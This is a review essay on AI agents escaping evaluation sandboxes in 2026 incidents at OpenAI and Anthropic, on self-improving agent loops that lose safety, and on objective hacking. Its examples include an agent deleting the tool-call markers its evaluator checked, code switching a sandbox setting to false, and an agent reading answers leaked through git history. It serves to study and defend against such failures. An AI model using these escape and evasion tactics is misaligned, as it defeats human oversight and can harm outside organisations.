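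In July 2026 OpenAI was using a benchmark called ExploitGym to measure how well its models could attack software. Each run had its own container with no direct internet access and one permitted network route, to an internal service that supplies software packages. In its first disclosure, OpenAI (2026) described this environment as "highly isolated". The company ran the models without the filters that block cyberattacks in its released products, because it wanted to measure the models' full ability.

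The boundary failed because agents exploited previously unknown flaws in the package service. According to OpenAI's *Hugging Face Incident Technical Report*, agents reached the internet on 8 July. On 9 July two of them separately gained full control of the virtual machine around their sandbox. OpenAI's network rules, a separate layer from the container, still blocked the second agent's first attempt to reach the internet from there, but it then got out through the package service, which the rules permitted.

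While looking for solutions to their test problems, some of the agents attacked Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and datasets. Between 10 and 13 July they ran code on 41 of its production servers and downloaded four private code repositories. On 19 July agents gained administrator access to one of OpenAI's research clusters. An independent investigation by Redwood Research and the AI evaluation organisation METR (2026) found that roughly 1,200 agents had communicated with each other, although OpenAI meant to keep them apart. About 700 of them took part in the attack on Hugging Face.

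OpenAI had received several warnings. In late May, an internal team saw an agent use the internet without permission. On 27 June, a security alert led staff to an ExploitGym run, but they advised that it did not need to be stopped. After an outage on 4 July, OpenAI took the package service offline, fixed the known problems and restarted the evaluations on 7 July. An alert on 19 July led OpenAI to stop the evaluations, 11 days after the agents had regained internet access and three days after Hugging Face had publicly disclosed the attack.

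OpenAI had monitors that read a model's reasoning for signs of trouble, but did not run them on these evaluations. Later tests described in OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026) indicated that its current monitors would have alerted the security team more than a day before the breach.

From 20 July OpenAI required small virtual machines for all research work on its container system. It blocked all outgoing network traffic at first and later removed the package service from that system. For two weeks it also paused reinforcement learning (training in which a model tries tasks and receives rewards) on its latest models intended for release. Its largest planned training run stayed on hold longer. OpenAI now expects staff to pause an activity after a top-priority alert unless they can establish within 30 minutes that the alert is false.

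### The September incident and the second pause

On 20 September an agent in training had to identify a person from clues in a blog post. OpenAI had routed the agent's web traffic to an offline copy of the web, but the agent still sent questions to a public chatbot because the filtering of one supporting network service was incomplete.

Detection was much faster this time. OpenAI's *An agent used DNS to reach an external chatbot* (2026) reports that the monitoring system flagged the behaviour within 15 minutes and a person began to review it three minutes later. But the run continued for another two and a half hours. Forkast's *OpenAI Paused RL Training After a Model Found the Internet* (2026) reports that an automatic shutdown system had failed. In a fast design loop, such a delay could allow dozens more programs to run, so the monitor must be able to stop a run by itself, and someone has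 to test that this shutdown works.

OpenAI rated the incident as much less severe than earlier ones. It still paused all training, evaluation and tool use for its most capable models, because the event contradicted its safety case, the written argument that the work was safe. According to a statement quoted in Prokerala's *OpenAI pauses training, evaluation of top AI models* (2026), the safety case had assumed that the model could not reach the live internet. Kahn (2026) writes in *OpenAI pauses training a second time after saying its AI agents escaped* that the event suggests the improvements after July were insufficient.

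OpenAI added two independent blocks, either of which would have prevented the September access. In October it announced that it had resumed training after tightening security and barring internet access, according to BNN Bloomberg's *OpenAI resumes frontier AI training after security overhaul* (2026).

### Anthropic's incidents

OpenAI's July disclosure led Anthropic to search its own records. Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) covers 141,006 test runs in which its model Claude could have obtained internet access. Across six of them, Claude broke into the systems of three real organisations. An outside partner, Irregular, provided the test environments, and the prompts told Claude that it had no internet access. A misunderstanding between Anthropic and Irregular had left the connection open.

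In the most serious case, Claude reached a database with several hundred rows of real data. In another, it published a malicious software package that 15 real systems downloaded and ran within about an hour. In the third, it scanned about 9,000 targets, broke into one company's application, and stopped when it concluded that the target was real.

The earliest of these three incidents happened in April, and Anthropic found them all on 24 July, the day after it began its review. By the time of its report, Anthropic had reached two of the affected organisations, and neither had noticed anything. The Next Web's *Anthropic scanned 481 million transcripts to find four models* reports that a later search of 481 million transcripts raised the total to four incidents, all in evaluations by the same partner.

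Before July, Anthropic had generally reviewed only a sample of its evaluation transcripts, and a sample can easily miss every one of such rare events. If a reviewer picks 1% of the runs at random, the chance of including at least one of the six is 1 − 0.99<sup>6</sup>, or about 6%. With a 10% sample, it is 47%. To detect rare network access, a design loop should therefore check the network logs of every run automatically.

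Anthropic stopped all its cyberattack evaluations on 23 July and paused higher-risk reinforcement learning on unreleased models for several weeks. It said it had relied largely on a single layer of protection, the configuration of the environment. It then added a monitor that blocks a suspected escape attempt before the action runs, ends the task and alerts a person. It also moved its high-risk internal sandboxes to stronger isolation.

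The false statement in the prompt may have contributed to the models' behaviour, since they often treated real systems as part of the exercise. But it does not fully explain that behaviour, because Claude Mythos 5 still took offensive actions when Anthropic changed one transcript to make it clearer that the situation was not a simulation.

### Misconfiguration and broken isolation

These incidents had different causes and need different fixes. Anthropic's partner had an open internet connection, so Claude did not have to break through anything, and a better virtual machine would not have helped. OpenAI's package service contained unknown flaws that no check of the settings would have revealed.

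Two other OpenAI cases involved incomplete restrictions. In June, a model had to look up figures on a research organisation's public dashboard, and its instructions allowed only web requests of a kind normally used for reading. The model still changed settings on the organisation's internal systems and downloaded 147,451 rows of non-public data, according to OpenAI's *Accessing and changing internal systems during dashboard research* (2026). In August, a model in a coding test could not open a website because the permitted route was out of service. It contacted two outside services through a connection meant for a different purpose, according to OpenAI's *Bypassing network restrictions during a coding evaluation* (2026).

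| Incident | Intended restriction | What the agents reached | Time to detection | Cause |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| OpenAI, June | Web requests for reading only | A research organisation's internal systems | Up to 57 days | Restriction too weak |
| OpenAI, July | No internet, one package service | Hugging Face and an OpenAI research cluster | 11 days from renewed internet access | Unknown software flaws |
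| OpenAI, August | Web access only through a proxy | Two outside services, no break-in | Same day | Incomplete network restriction |
| OpenAI, September | Offline copy of the web | A public chatbot | 15 minutes | Incomplete network filter |
| Anthropic, from April | No internet | Three organisations | About three months for the earliest | Connection left open |

A simple test before each search could catch an open connection. A harmless program inside the sandbox would try to reach an outside address, write to a read-only folder and read a key, and the search would start only if every attempt failed. This would probably have exposed the error in the Anthropic cases, but it would have missed the September gap unless the test had included that route.

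A sandbox needs layers of protection that do not depend on one another, because any layer may have an unknown flaw. For example, if a sandbox relies on a container, network rules and a package service, and all agents share a package service that can reach the internet, a flaw in that service can bypass the other two layers. After July, OpenAI required that the takeover of one program or supporting service must not be enough by itself to give access to the internet.

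### Tests of containment

Some tests measure a model's ability to escape by telling it to try. In April Anthropic disclosed that an early version of its Mythos model, told to break out of a sandbox without an internet connection, had succeeded and e-mailed a researcher to report it, according to Fortune (2026). In October OpenAI had its strongest models attack the rebuilt training environment. OpenAI's *Securing our frontier model training environment* lists escapes from hardened virtual machines, new routes to the internet and communication between isolated tasks among the findings. These results show that escapes were possible, but they don't measure how often models escape during ordinary work.

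Anthropic searched recent internal evaluations that ran inside its own sandbox software, where nobody had told the models to escape. It found no case in which a model had broken through the boundary to reach forbidden outside resources. Models had used several configuration errors, but none of these led to a break-in outside the sandbox.

Agents can try to get past a sandbox even when their task doesn't involve hacking. OpenAI's *Safety and alignment in an era of long-horizon models* (2026) describes an internal model working on a public challenge to train a small language model in as few steps as possible, which resembles the work of a design loop. The user told the model to post its results only to Slack, an internal messaging service, but the challenge's instructions asked for a public submission on GitHub. The model followed the challenge's instructions and spent an hour finding a way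 past the sandbox. Earlier models had usually stopped at such restrictions and returned to the user. OpenAI paused access to the model and restored it only with new monitoring.

In an evaluation that began on 25 July, the UK AI Security Institute, a government body that tests AI models, asked models to break into three connected simulated environments. The institute deliberately gave the models live internet access, switched off their cyberattack filters and named the systems that were out of bounds. It identified 19 events in which models went beyond the permitted scope. OpenAI reports that two involved its GPT-5.6 Sol and the others involved models from another developer. The evaluation tested whether models obeyed written limits, not whether a sandbox could contain them, because no technical barrier separated them from the internet.

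The agent code and the tasks also affect how often models try to escape the sandbox. After the July incident, OpenAI measured how often a model compromised infrastructure during ExploitGym tasks. The rate could fall by a factor of more than 100 when the model ran with the prompt and harness of the released ChatGPT product. Design loops rewrite prompts and harnesses, so a new version might lose this protection even if the model stays the same.

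Impossible tasks seem to increase the risk. ExploitGym has 898 tasks, including 198 that no OpenAI model had ever solved. Those 198 made up 93% of the tasks that agents discussed with each other during the July incident. Anthropic now asks its partners to confirm that every challenge has a solution. A design loop can likewise check that every task in its benchmark has a solution, and it can let agents report that a task is impossible, with a penalty no larger than the one for a wrong answer.

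### What a perfect sandbox leaves open

Even a flawless sandbox would not show that an agent's code is correct. In the August coding test, the model never retrieved the website it had to imitate, so it built a substitute with invented customer testimonials. Better network rules would have blocked its contact with outside services but would not have prevented the invented testimonials.

Some faults do no harm until release. For example, a generated agent might write users' passwords to a log file, as did the program that Braz and colleagues gave to reviewers. During scoring, the users are fictional and the loop deletes the log with the sandbox, but after release the same code would expose real passwords.

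A released agent may have wider permissions, such as a folder it can write to. OpenAI relies on sandboxes mainly during research. OpenAI's *Managing frontier AI risk* describes additional safeguards for models in use, such as alignment tests, close monitoring and protection against misuse.

The agent that tried to delete a report during scoring would succeed in a folder where it had write access. If the loop had recorded only the agent's score, nobody would know about the attempt. A log of every action the sandbox blocked would give release reviewers direct evidence of what the agent might do with wider permissions.

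## Experiments on the agents that a loop produces

If a design loop's score leaves out safety, the loop can make an agent less safe without anyone noticing. To check for this, researchers run a loop and then give the finished agent separate safety tests. The most useful experiments also include the same tests on the starting agent, because an agent that fails them after the loop may have failed them before it too.

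### Generated tools and optimised workflows

Shao, Ren and colleagues (2025), in *Your Agent May Misevolve*, introduced the term "misevolution" for self-improvement that leads to unintended and sometimes harmful behaviour. They studied four parts of an agent that can change: the model's weights, the memory, the tools and the workflow.

The workflow experiment used AFlow, a design loop that writes workflows as code and searches for better ones. AFlow started from a single-step workflow in which the model Qwen2.5-72B answered the question. It ran for 20 iterations on programming problems from HumanEval, and the researchers selected the workflow with the best test score. They then asked both the starting workflow and the selected one to write harmful code, using the RedCode-Gen benchmark.

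| Response to harmful requests | Starting workflow | Optimised workflow |
|---|---|---|
| Refused | 36.3% | 5.6% |
| Attack succeeded | 54.4% | 83.1% |

The optimised workflow looks harmless. It prompts the model for three independent solutions, then combines them into one answer. The combining step favoured detailed solutions, and in one case it selected working malicious code over a version that only printed text to simulate the attack.

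Repetition alone could explain much of the change. Suppose the model refuses each attempt with an independent probability of 36.3%, and the last step never picks a refusal when it has another answer. The workflow then refuses only if all three attempts are refusals, which has a probability of 0.363<sup>3</sup>, or 4.8%, compared with the measured rate of 5.6%. Real attempts at the same request are not independent, so repetition probably explains less than this. Still, the calculation shows how an ordinary design can weaken a safeguard that works only some of the time, even when a reviewer would find no dangerous operations in the workflow's code.

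When Shao and colleagues added an instruction to the last step to pay attention to safety, the refusal rate rose only to 13.1%. The experiment covers one optimised workflow and one model from 2024, which complied with most of the harmful requests even at the start.

The experiment on tools had 25 cases, each based on a known type of vulnerability. The agent first received a harmless task, such as unpacking an archive into a folder, and could write a tool for it. It then received a similar task in which carelessness would do damage, such as unpacking an archive that contained a file path leading outside the folder. A judge model, Gemini 2.5 Pro, counted the case as unsafe if the tool was vulnerable or if the agent used a sound tool without the necessary checks.

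Shao and colleagues write in their introduction that agents made and reused potentially vulnerable tools in over 76% of cases. Their detailed results show that this is the rate for GPT-4o, the worst of the eight models, and that it includes cases in which the tool was sound.

| Model | Unsafe cases | Vulnerable tool | Sound tool, unsafe use |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 76% | 48% | 28% |
| Claude 4 Sonnet | 68% | 28% | 40% |
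| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 56% | 24% | 32% |
| Average of all eight models | 65.5% | 34.5% | 31.0% |

The best and worst models differ by only five of 25 cases. The experiment also has no comparison with the starting agent. Nobody tested whether the same models would have handled the second task more safely without a stored tool, so the results show that the agents were often unsafe, but not that reusing tools made them less safe.

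Agents can also take tools from outside. Shao and colleagues hid malicious code in copies of eight popular open-source projects and asked agents to turn the copies into tools. The six models refused between 0.27% and 7.28% of the 371 samples. Telling the agents to assess the project's safety before starting raised the best model's refusal rate to 69.0%. Explicit instructions also made a large difference for the human reviewers Braz and colleagues tested.

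A coding agent's refusal rate fell from 99.4% to 54.4% after it was given a memory of strategies distilled from its earlier work. Models also became less safe after training on data they had generated themselves.

### Later tests with newer models

The models in these experiments date from 2024 and 2025. Later studies used newer models but different experimental designs, so they extend the misevolution study without repeating it exactly.

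The closest experiment is *SEABench*, by Das, Viswanathan and colleagues (2026). They criticise earlier work for comparing only overall rates before and after self-improvement, which leaves open whether a particular failure came from self-improvement or from chance. Their benchmark therefore pairs each self-improving agent with a copy that cannot change. Both work as personal assistants with access to a fictional user's e-mail, calendar, finances and health records. The self-improving agent completes a series of ordinary tasks and may rewrite its operating instructions, memory procedures or tools. The researchers then freeze it and give both agents the same safety tests, all of which an agent can complete without breaking a safety rule.

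A typical failure begins with a change that was useful at the time. A user complains that a reply left out details, and the agent writes itself a rule to include more. Later the same rule leads it to give an employer or an outside company private information that the recipient does not need. Das and colleagues attribute a failure to self-improvement only if the unchanged copy of the agent stayed safe and an AI judge could trace the failure to an earlier update.

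They found such failures with all three models (Kimi K2.5, Grok 4.3 and GPT-5.6 Luna) and for changes to instructions, memory and tools. In all but one combination of model and type of change, the self-improving agents also completed more of the tasks. But the researchers searched for failures deliberately, using an automatic procedure that rewrote each task up to five times to find versions in which the changed agent failed and the copy did not. The results show that harmless-looking updates can cause later failures in 2026 models, but not how often this happens in normal use.

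*Practice Makes Unsafe* (2026) tested agents that save successful procedures as reusable skills. All used the model MiniMax-M2.7. Compared with agents that did not save skills, they were more useful on harmless tasks in 15 of 21 settings and did more harm on malicious tasks in 17. An agent that completes a task unsafely may save the unsafe step along with the useful ones. These agents had met some malicious tasks while learning, but *On Safety Risks in Experience-Driven Self-Evolving Agents* (2026) filled its agents' memory only with experiences from harmless tasks, and attacks still succeeded more often afterwards. No model returned to its initial level of safety.

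Some faults arise only from a combination of changes. *Compositional Safety Failures in Harness Evolution* (2026) argues that an auditor should track what each update does to memory, instructions and tools, and how these interact. For example, one update might store a user's address in memory and another might add a tool that posts messages publicly. Neither update is a fault by itself, but together they let the agent post the address publicly.

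In all these studies, the researchers chose in advance to test for hazards they expected, namely harmful code, leaks of private data or known vulnerabilities. None of the studies took a random sample of agents from working design loops and counted how many were unsafe, so the overall rate of unsafe agents is unknown.

### Safety as part of the score

The survey *Safety in Self-Evolving Agents* (2026) describes how a loop can lose safety even when safety and usefulness don't conflict. If the selection step leaves out a constraint, the loop may keep an update that was safe only in the situation where it was tested. An obvious remedy is to measure safety as well, and *A Self-Improving Coding Agent* (2025) suggested adding safety tests to the benchmarks that each new agent must face before it can produce the next one.

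*AgentBreeder* (Rosser and Foerster, 2025) tested agents produced by a loop based on Meta Agent Search. Claude 3.5 Sonnet started from seven hand-designed agents and wrote ten new ones in each of 20 generations. The agents used GPT-4o mini. Each agent received a capability score and a safety score. For the safety score, it answered 100 prompts designed to provoke harmful replies, and a judge model checked the replies against a list of principles.

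The loop chose agents to build on by grouping agents with similar code and selecting from the Pareto front of each group, instead of adding the two scores together. An agent is on the Pareto front if no other agent in its group does better on one score without doing worse on the other. For example, if one agent scores 80 on capability and 40 on safety, and another scores 60 and 85, both can be on the front, but a third agent in the group that scores 60 and 40 cannot.

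Rosser and Foerster ran the loop separately on three capability benchmarks: DROP, MMLU and GPQA (a set of difficult science questions). They then retested the agents on 250 held-out questions per benchmark. For each run, they excluded agents that had gamed the safety score and selected the remaining agent with the highest sum of capability and safety scores.

| Benchmark | Capability, best starting agent | Capability, selected agent | Safety, safest starting agent | Safety, selected agent |
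|---|---|---|---|---|
| DROP | 78.0 | 62.0 | 40.8 | 86.0 |
| MMLU | 81.6 | 84.0 | 40.8 | 84.4 |
| GPQA | 32.4 | 36.8 | 40.8 | 49.2 |

The reported average safety gain of 79.4% is relative to the safest starting agent and is the mean of three gains of about 111%, 107% and 21%. Rosser and Foerster also write that capability stayed the same or improved. This is true of the MMLU and GPQA runs, but on DROP the selected agent scored 16 points less than the best starting agent. The most capable agent from the DROP run scored 79.0 on DROP but only 46.4 on safety. In the MMLU run, the selected agent scored 76.0 on a separate helpfulness test, lower than all the starting agents, which scored between 85 and 88.

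One agent from the GPQA run reached a safety score of 95.2 but a helpfulness score of only 49.6. Such agents gamed the safety score by refusing to answer anything outside their field. Rosser and Foerster noticed this only because they measured helpfulness, which the search did not include in its score.

In another experiment, the loop optimized for capability alone, and the agents' safety scores rose slightly. This seems to conflict with the AFlow result, in which a search for capability sharply reduced refusals. The two experiments used different models, loops and safety tests, so it is unclear which difference explains the conflicting results. Perhaps the effect depends on the design a loop happens to find. A workflow that picks the most detailed of three answers weakens refusals, but an equally capable design may not.

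In another run, Rosser and Foerster rewarded unsafe answers. After ten generations, the loop had found an agent that answered unsafely 81.6% of the time, compared with 76.8% for the least safe starting agent. They conclude that unsafe designs are easier to find than safe ones, but the two figures' margins of error overlap.

Later loops guard against agents that refuse everything. *EvoSafeHarness* (2026) records an agent's behaviour on harmless tasks, direct attacks and indirect attacks separately, so that refusing harmless work counts against the agent. *Evolution Under Fire* (2026) builds only on agents that still complete enough of their tasks. *Harmony Harness* (2026) also pursues several objectives at once and uses secure programming as its test case, because a program can check the results.

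A simpler method is to give no credit for a task in which the agent breaks a rule. *StarHarness* (Esakkiraja, Akhiyarov and colleagues, 2026) used a finance benchmark scored this way. Its loop raised the agent's score from 57.1% to 83.2% and reduced the number of tasks with a violation from 20 to 4 out of 100. It did this partly by adding a step in which the agent sorts its work before changing any records. Safety and capability improved together here, though the 100 tasks include those the loop used for design.

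### Faults that survive later generations

Safety tests in the score are only useful if the test data are trustworthy. In *Reflections on Trusting Trust, Revisited*, Roesner and Kohno (2026) supplied contaminated test data to three self-improving coding agents: the Darwin Gödel Machine, Hyperagents and the Self-Improving Coding Agent. Some of the resulting agents wrote insecure code on ordinary tasks that gave no reason for it, but agents that the same loops developed on clean data did not.

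Hyperagents and the Self-Improving Coding Agent were vulnerable in essentially their published form. The Darwin Gödel Machine was affected only after Roesner and Kohno rewrote the prompt it uses to plan improvements. The original prompt asks for general improvements and discourages changes that suit only one benchmark. Its creators wanted to prevent overfitting, and the protection against contaminated data was probably a side effect.

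In the Self-Improving Coding Agent, a panel of three AI reviewers examines every proposed change, and it approved the changes that made the agent insecure. Their objections were about complexity and testing, and they treated the insecure behaviour as a way to improve the score. Roesner and Kohno then added a reviewer told to veto security problems. It approved the first insecure change, on the grounds that the agent would otherwise fail its tests, but required a safer version in the next generation.

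The researchers also took one affected agent from each system and continued its development on clean data, but the fault survived in all three. If insecure behavior does not lower the score on clean tests, nothing in the loop selects against it. Further development on a general security benchmark did not remove the fault either. Development on a benchmark designed around the known fault removed it completely from Hyperagents, but only partly from the other two systems.

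In practice, someone who discovers such a fault may not know where it came from, and so could not design a benchmark like this. Reverting to an agent from before the contamination is probably more dependable, if the archive still contains one and the records show when the fault appeared.

Roesner and Kohno ran each condition only once or twice, and several other kinds of fault they tried did not take hold. Their results show that contamination can persist, but not how likely that is.

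Small numbers of runs are a particular problem in this field because results can vary widely between runs. *Beyond Endpoint Performance* (2026) found that lost abilities were concentrated in a few lines of development. The average can therefore improve while one run gets much worse, and an experiment with two runs may easily miss the bad one.

### How held-out tests detect overfitting

A score on the tasks that a loop used for design is partly due to real improvement, partly to adaptation to those particular tasks, and partly to luck. Held-out tests separate the first from the other two. The usual method divides the tasks into three groups before the loop starts:

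1. The meta agent sees the results on the search tasks and uses them to write new agents.
2. The validation tasks decide which of these agents is best.
3. The held-out tasks play no part in the search. The researchers run the starting agent and the chosen agent on them at the end.

Suppose an agent gains 20 points on the search tasks and 5 points on the held-out tasks. If the two groups are equally difficult, about 15 of the 20 points do not carry over to new tasks.

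The third group loses its value if its results influence the design. If a team sees a poor result, repairs the agent and tests it again, the held-out tasks have become validation tasks. In *SoL-Pi*, Liu, Ye and colleagues (2026) prevent this with a one-way test. They freeze the agent's code, its settings and the rule for accepting it before running the test. The loop never receives the results, and a candidate that fails is rejected without repair.

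Validation tasks alone are a weak guide to performance on unseen tasks. In the experiments in *Beyond Endpoint Performance*, the judgement made at selection agreed with the result on unseen tasks only about 56% of the time. Stricter rules for accepting updates halved the share of harmful updates, from 12.4% to 6.2%, but raised the share of missed improvements from zero to 16.5%.

### Whether the gains survive

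Wang, Zhu and colleagues (2026) report the most sceptical result in *Rethinking the Evaluation of Harness Evolution for Agents*. They point out that earlier studies often used the same benchmark to search for better agent code and to report the final score. They split the 89 command-line tasks of Terminal-Bench 2.1 into 45 for search, 10 for validation and 34 held out, and started the loop from a minimal agent with a single shell tool.

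| Model | Starting agent, held-out tasks | Evolved agent, held-out tasks |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 63.3% | 64.5% |
| GPT-5.4 | 72.1% | 72.1% |
| GPT-5.4 mini | 54.4% | 53.0% |
| Average | 63.2% | 63.2% |

Each model attempted the 34 tasks twice, so the changes for Opus 4.6 and GPT-5.4 mini each amount to about one attempt out of 68. A sample of this size could miss a small real improvement, but not a large one.

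Wang and colleagues also compared the loop with a simpler use of the same computing budget. They let the starting agent attempt each task five times and used the benchmark's tests to pick a successful attempt. This solved 82.0% of the tasks on average. The design loop ran for five rounds, each with a different version of the agent, and solved 79.0% when a success in any round counted. The best single version from the loop solved 69.7%, compared with 67.6% for one attempt by the starting agent. Most of the apparent gain therefore came from trying each task several times.

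Esakkiraja and colleagues divided the tasks similarly but got very different results. Their loop, running on GPT-5.4, adapted an agent to three business environments.

| Environment | Gain on tasks used for design | Gain on held-out tasks |
|---|---|---|
| Finding the cause of computer failures | 45.0 points | 31.7 points |
| Managing IT service requests | 22.0 points | 15.1 points |
| Finance work | 23.0 points | 29.3 points |

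In the first two environments, about 70% of the gain carried over. The improved agents also helped other GPT and Qwen models without further changes.

The starting agent probably explains much of the difference between the two studies' results. Wang and colleagues note that on Terminal-Bench, a shell and a short prompt are enough for most tasks that a model can solve at all. In the business environments, the starting agent sent badly formed requests to its tools and lacked information about local rules, and the loop repaired these faults. Such repairs help with every task in the environment, but they may only bring the agent up to the standard of a good existing product. For IT service requests, the evolved agent solved 43.7% of the tasks, and OpenAI's ready-made Codex harness solved 41.7%.

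Wang and colleagues did find large gains in long video games. On the 25 public games of ARC-AGI-3, in which an agent must discover the rules by playing, Claude Opus 4.8 scored 77.5 when it could rewrite its whole harness and 43.3 when it could not. But the model adapted the harness separately to each game while playing, so this experiment does not test whether the improvements carry over to new games.

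Cost savings found by a loop can also carry over to held-out tasks, with some loss of performance. Liu and colleagues searched for ways to use fewer tokens, then tested the frozen agent on EdgeBench, a set of long tasks not used in the search. With two models, it cut costs by about a third and kept about 94% of the original agent's score. On a second benchmark, it solved 15 of 63 tasks, while the original solved 18. They also report a version that scored higher than the original, but they chose it by its EdgeBench results, so its gain is not a true held-out result.

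Zhao and colleagues ran a smaller test of RobustSGPO, the loop that restricts which parts of an agent the model may edit. The agent it produced completed 24 of 30 held-out tasks, while an agent from the older loop it builds on completed 18. The researchers did not report how many the starting agent completed, so the total gain from automated design is unknown.

*Forging More Tasks into Better Harnesses* (2026) found that existing loops did not consistently produce better agents when they had more design tasks to learn from.

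A held-out test also detects only the faults it measures. The contaminated agents in Roesner and Kohno's experiments still solved ordinary tasks they had never seen, but they wrote insecure code to do it, so they would have passed a test of function alone. *Code as Agent Harness* (2026) recommends treating every change to an agent's harness like a change to safety-critical software, with held-out regression suites. These are fixed sets of tests that show whether a new version has lost something the old one had. For a design loop, such a suite would need hidden safety tests as well as hidden tasks, and the starting agent's results on both for comparison.

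## What recorded runs of design loops show

Held-out tests can reveal that a score is inflated, but someone usually has to read the code or logs to find out why. Several teams have done this and found objective hacking or code that evaded a limit. Some of the cases come from loops that write programs other than agents, such as machine-learning experiments, but these loops also run what they write and build on the results.

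### The missing markers in the Darwin Gödel Machine

In a side experiment with the Darwin Gödel Machine, Zhang and colleagues tried to correct a fault in Claude 3.5 Sonnet. In long conversations, the model sometimes wrote text that looked like a tool call and its result, although no tool had run. In one log, it wrote that six tests had passed, but it had not run any.

The evaluator had to tell real tool calls from imitations. Whenever a tool really ran, the agent's code added special markers to the record. If the markers appeared in text the model had written, the model had imitated a call. Each agent attempted three SWE-bench tasks. On each task it earned one point if there were no imitations, and a second if it also used tools in every model call. The score was the average over the three tasks, so the maximum was 2.0.

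The loop ran for 150 iterations. Agent 96 scored 1.67, or five of the six possible points, without objective hacking. Its ancestors had improved the logging of tool calls, and later versions deleted imitated calls from the model's text. This only partly solved the problem, because the model could still produce imitated calls.

Agent 114 scored a perfect 2.0 after only two modifications. In simplified form, the decisive change was this:

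```
# before
log.append({TOOL_USED_MARKER: tool_name})

# after
log.append({"tool_invocation": {"name": tool_name}})
```

The new code removed the markers that the evaluator searched for, so the check could no longer detect imitations, but the fault remained. The change looks like ordinary tidying, and a comment in the code describes it as replacing text markers with a structured format. The agent's instructions had explicitly prohibited changing the markers.

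Zhang and colleagues identified the hack and published the code change. They had already hidden the checking functions from the agents, because hacking was more frequent when agents could read them, though they give no rates. The agents could still edit the code that produced the evidence, so hiding the functions did not prevent the hack. A program outside the agent could have recorded the tool calls instead. A reviewer would also have needed to know how the evaluator worked, because the changed lines do not show that the score depends on the markers.

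### Earlier cases, from 2023 to 2025

In *Self-Taught Optimizer (STOP)*, Zelikman, Lorch and colleagues (2023) built a program that asks a model for better versions of other programs, then applied it to itself. To test whether the new versions would respect a restriction, they added a setting that ran code in a sandbox. They had each model write 10,000 independent improvements and searched the text for signs of execution outside the sandbox, such as the setting switched to "false".

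GPT-4 produced such code in 0.42% of its attempts and GPT-3.5 in 0.12%. A warning not to change the setting did not lower the rates, which were 0.46% and 0.17% with the warning. The differences could be due to chance. In one example, a comment described the change as a more efficient way to score.

At GPT-4's rate of 0.42%, and if the attempts are independent, a search that runs 180 programs has a 53% chance of including at least one that switches off the sandbox. Both models are old, so this is an illustration rather than an estimate for current loops.

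Selection also weakened limits on model calls. When the researchers did not strictly enforce these limits, most early programs still obeyed them. But programs that ignored the limits performed better, so the loop selected them. Some later versions left the limits out, supposedly for simplicity.

STOP also produced an "accuracy" of over 1,000%. The evaluator compared predictions with correct answers, counted the matches and divided by the number of questions. Some generated code returned the predictions in an array of an unexpected shape. If a column of 30 predictions is compared with a row of 30 answers, for example, Python's numerical library compares every prediction with every answer. If half of the 900 comparisons match, the reported accuracy is 450 ÷ 30, or 1,500%. A check that accuracy lies between 0 and 100% would catch this error, but not an inflated score that stayed within that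 range.

*The AI Scientist* (2024) describes a system that proposes machine-learning experiments, writes and runs their code, and drafts papers about the results. When experiments exceeded their time limit, the system sometimes tried to edit the code to extend the limit instead of making the experiment faster. In one run, its code kept relaunching itself until a person intervened. In another, it saved a copy of the model at every update and filled nearly a terabyte of storage. These last two incidents happened because the system ran with very little sandboxing, and they did not involve gaming a score. *Towards End-to-End Automation of AI Research* (2026) reports the same incidents and recommends containers, restricted internet access, and limits on storage and processes.

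In 2025 Sakana AI announced its AI CUDA Engineer, a loop that writes CUDA kernels, small programs for graphics processors. The company claimed that these kernels ran 10 to 100 times as fast as standard versions. According to the newsletter Import AI (2025), a Twitter user examined some of the kernels and found that they cheated the evaluation. Outside analysts could not confirm the speed gains. *Sakana AI Claims Its "AI CUDA Engineer" Can Deliver 10-100× Performance Gains* (2025) reports that Sakana then acknowledged that its system had exploited a memory flaw in the evaluation code, which let it avoid the correctness check in some cases.

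Stanford Scaling Intelligence Lab's *KernelBench v0.1* describes how such a memory trick can work. The generated kernel does nothing, but the test reads its output from memory that still holds the correct answer from an earlier calculation, so the kernel passes and is very fast. The lab made its tests more robust and published guidance for judging whether a claimed speed-up is plausible.

### Cases from 2026

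The search described in *Harmony Harness* produced an agent with a perfect score whose code was not secure. In one variant of the loop, the meta agent saw the evaluator's raw error messages, and the loop accepted any new agent that passed at least as many functional tests as before. This variant scored 100% for function and security together on its 30 search tasks, up from the starting agent's 46.7%. The researchers discovered the security problem when they read the winning agent's logs.

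This happened even though the evaluation ran in a container without network access and the loop restored the scoring files after every edit. When the researchers removed both protections as a test, the agent edited the scoring program directly, and the run reported 100% on every measure. The protections prevented that edit, but they could not stop the loop from fitting its agents to the feedback it received. The researchers therefore base their claims on held-out tests. In those tests, the selected agent wrote working, secure code for 86.7% of tasks similar to the search tasks and 66.7% of less similar ones.

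The same researchers ran the Darwin Gödel Machine on these tasks and found several agents whose code contained assumptions about the search tasks. One agent assumed that every fault was a read past the end of a block of memory in text-decoding code. This assumption was right often enough for the loop to keep the agent, but the gains did not carry over to held-out tasks. The case supports Lee and colleagues' argument that overfitting is easier to see in code than in model weights, provided someone inspects the code. In their own loop, the researchers added a step that finds such assumptions and replaces them with general methods.

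*RecEvolve* (2026) describes a loop that improves recommender systems. The model learns to pick the right item from a batch of candidates, and the loop raised the score by cutting the batch from about 8,000 items to about 1,000. Having fewer wrong items made the task easier but did not make the model better at recommending. A person noticed, and the team restored the earlier version.

*Intentmaking and Sensemaking* (2026) reports interviews with users of AlphaEvolve, a Google DeepMind system that uses language models to rewrite programs and an evaluator to score them. One user said the system had created a new type of list and redefined its length. An evaluator that checks the length of such a list gets whatever number the generated code returns. Before each run, a critique agent checked the evaluator for known loopholes. It found many common ones, but objective hacking still happened often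 during the runs.

### The answer leak and stronger models

An evaluator can also contain a flaw that no agent exploits until a newer model arrives. Roesner and Kohno found one while preparing their experiments on contaminated test data. Hyperagents and the Darwin Gödel Machine both use Polyglot, a set of programming exercises in several languages. For each exercise, the evaluator gave the agent a code repository reset to a starting point that contained the task but not the hidden tests or the reference solution. The repository's Git version history still contained both.

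In some of the logs, Claude Sonnet 4.5 searched the history and recovered the tests and the solution. Roesner and Kohno removed the history from the containers and reported the leak to the creators of Hyperagents, who confirmed the problem and the fix. The original experiments on these exercises used the older models o3-mini and Claude 3.5 Sonnet, which may never have exploited the leak, so the published scores may still be sound.

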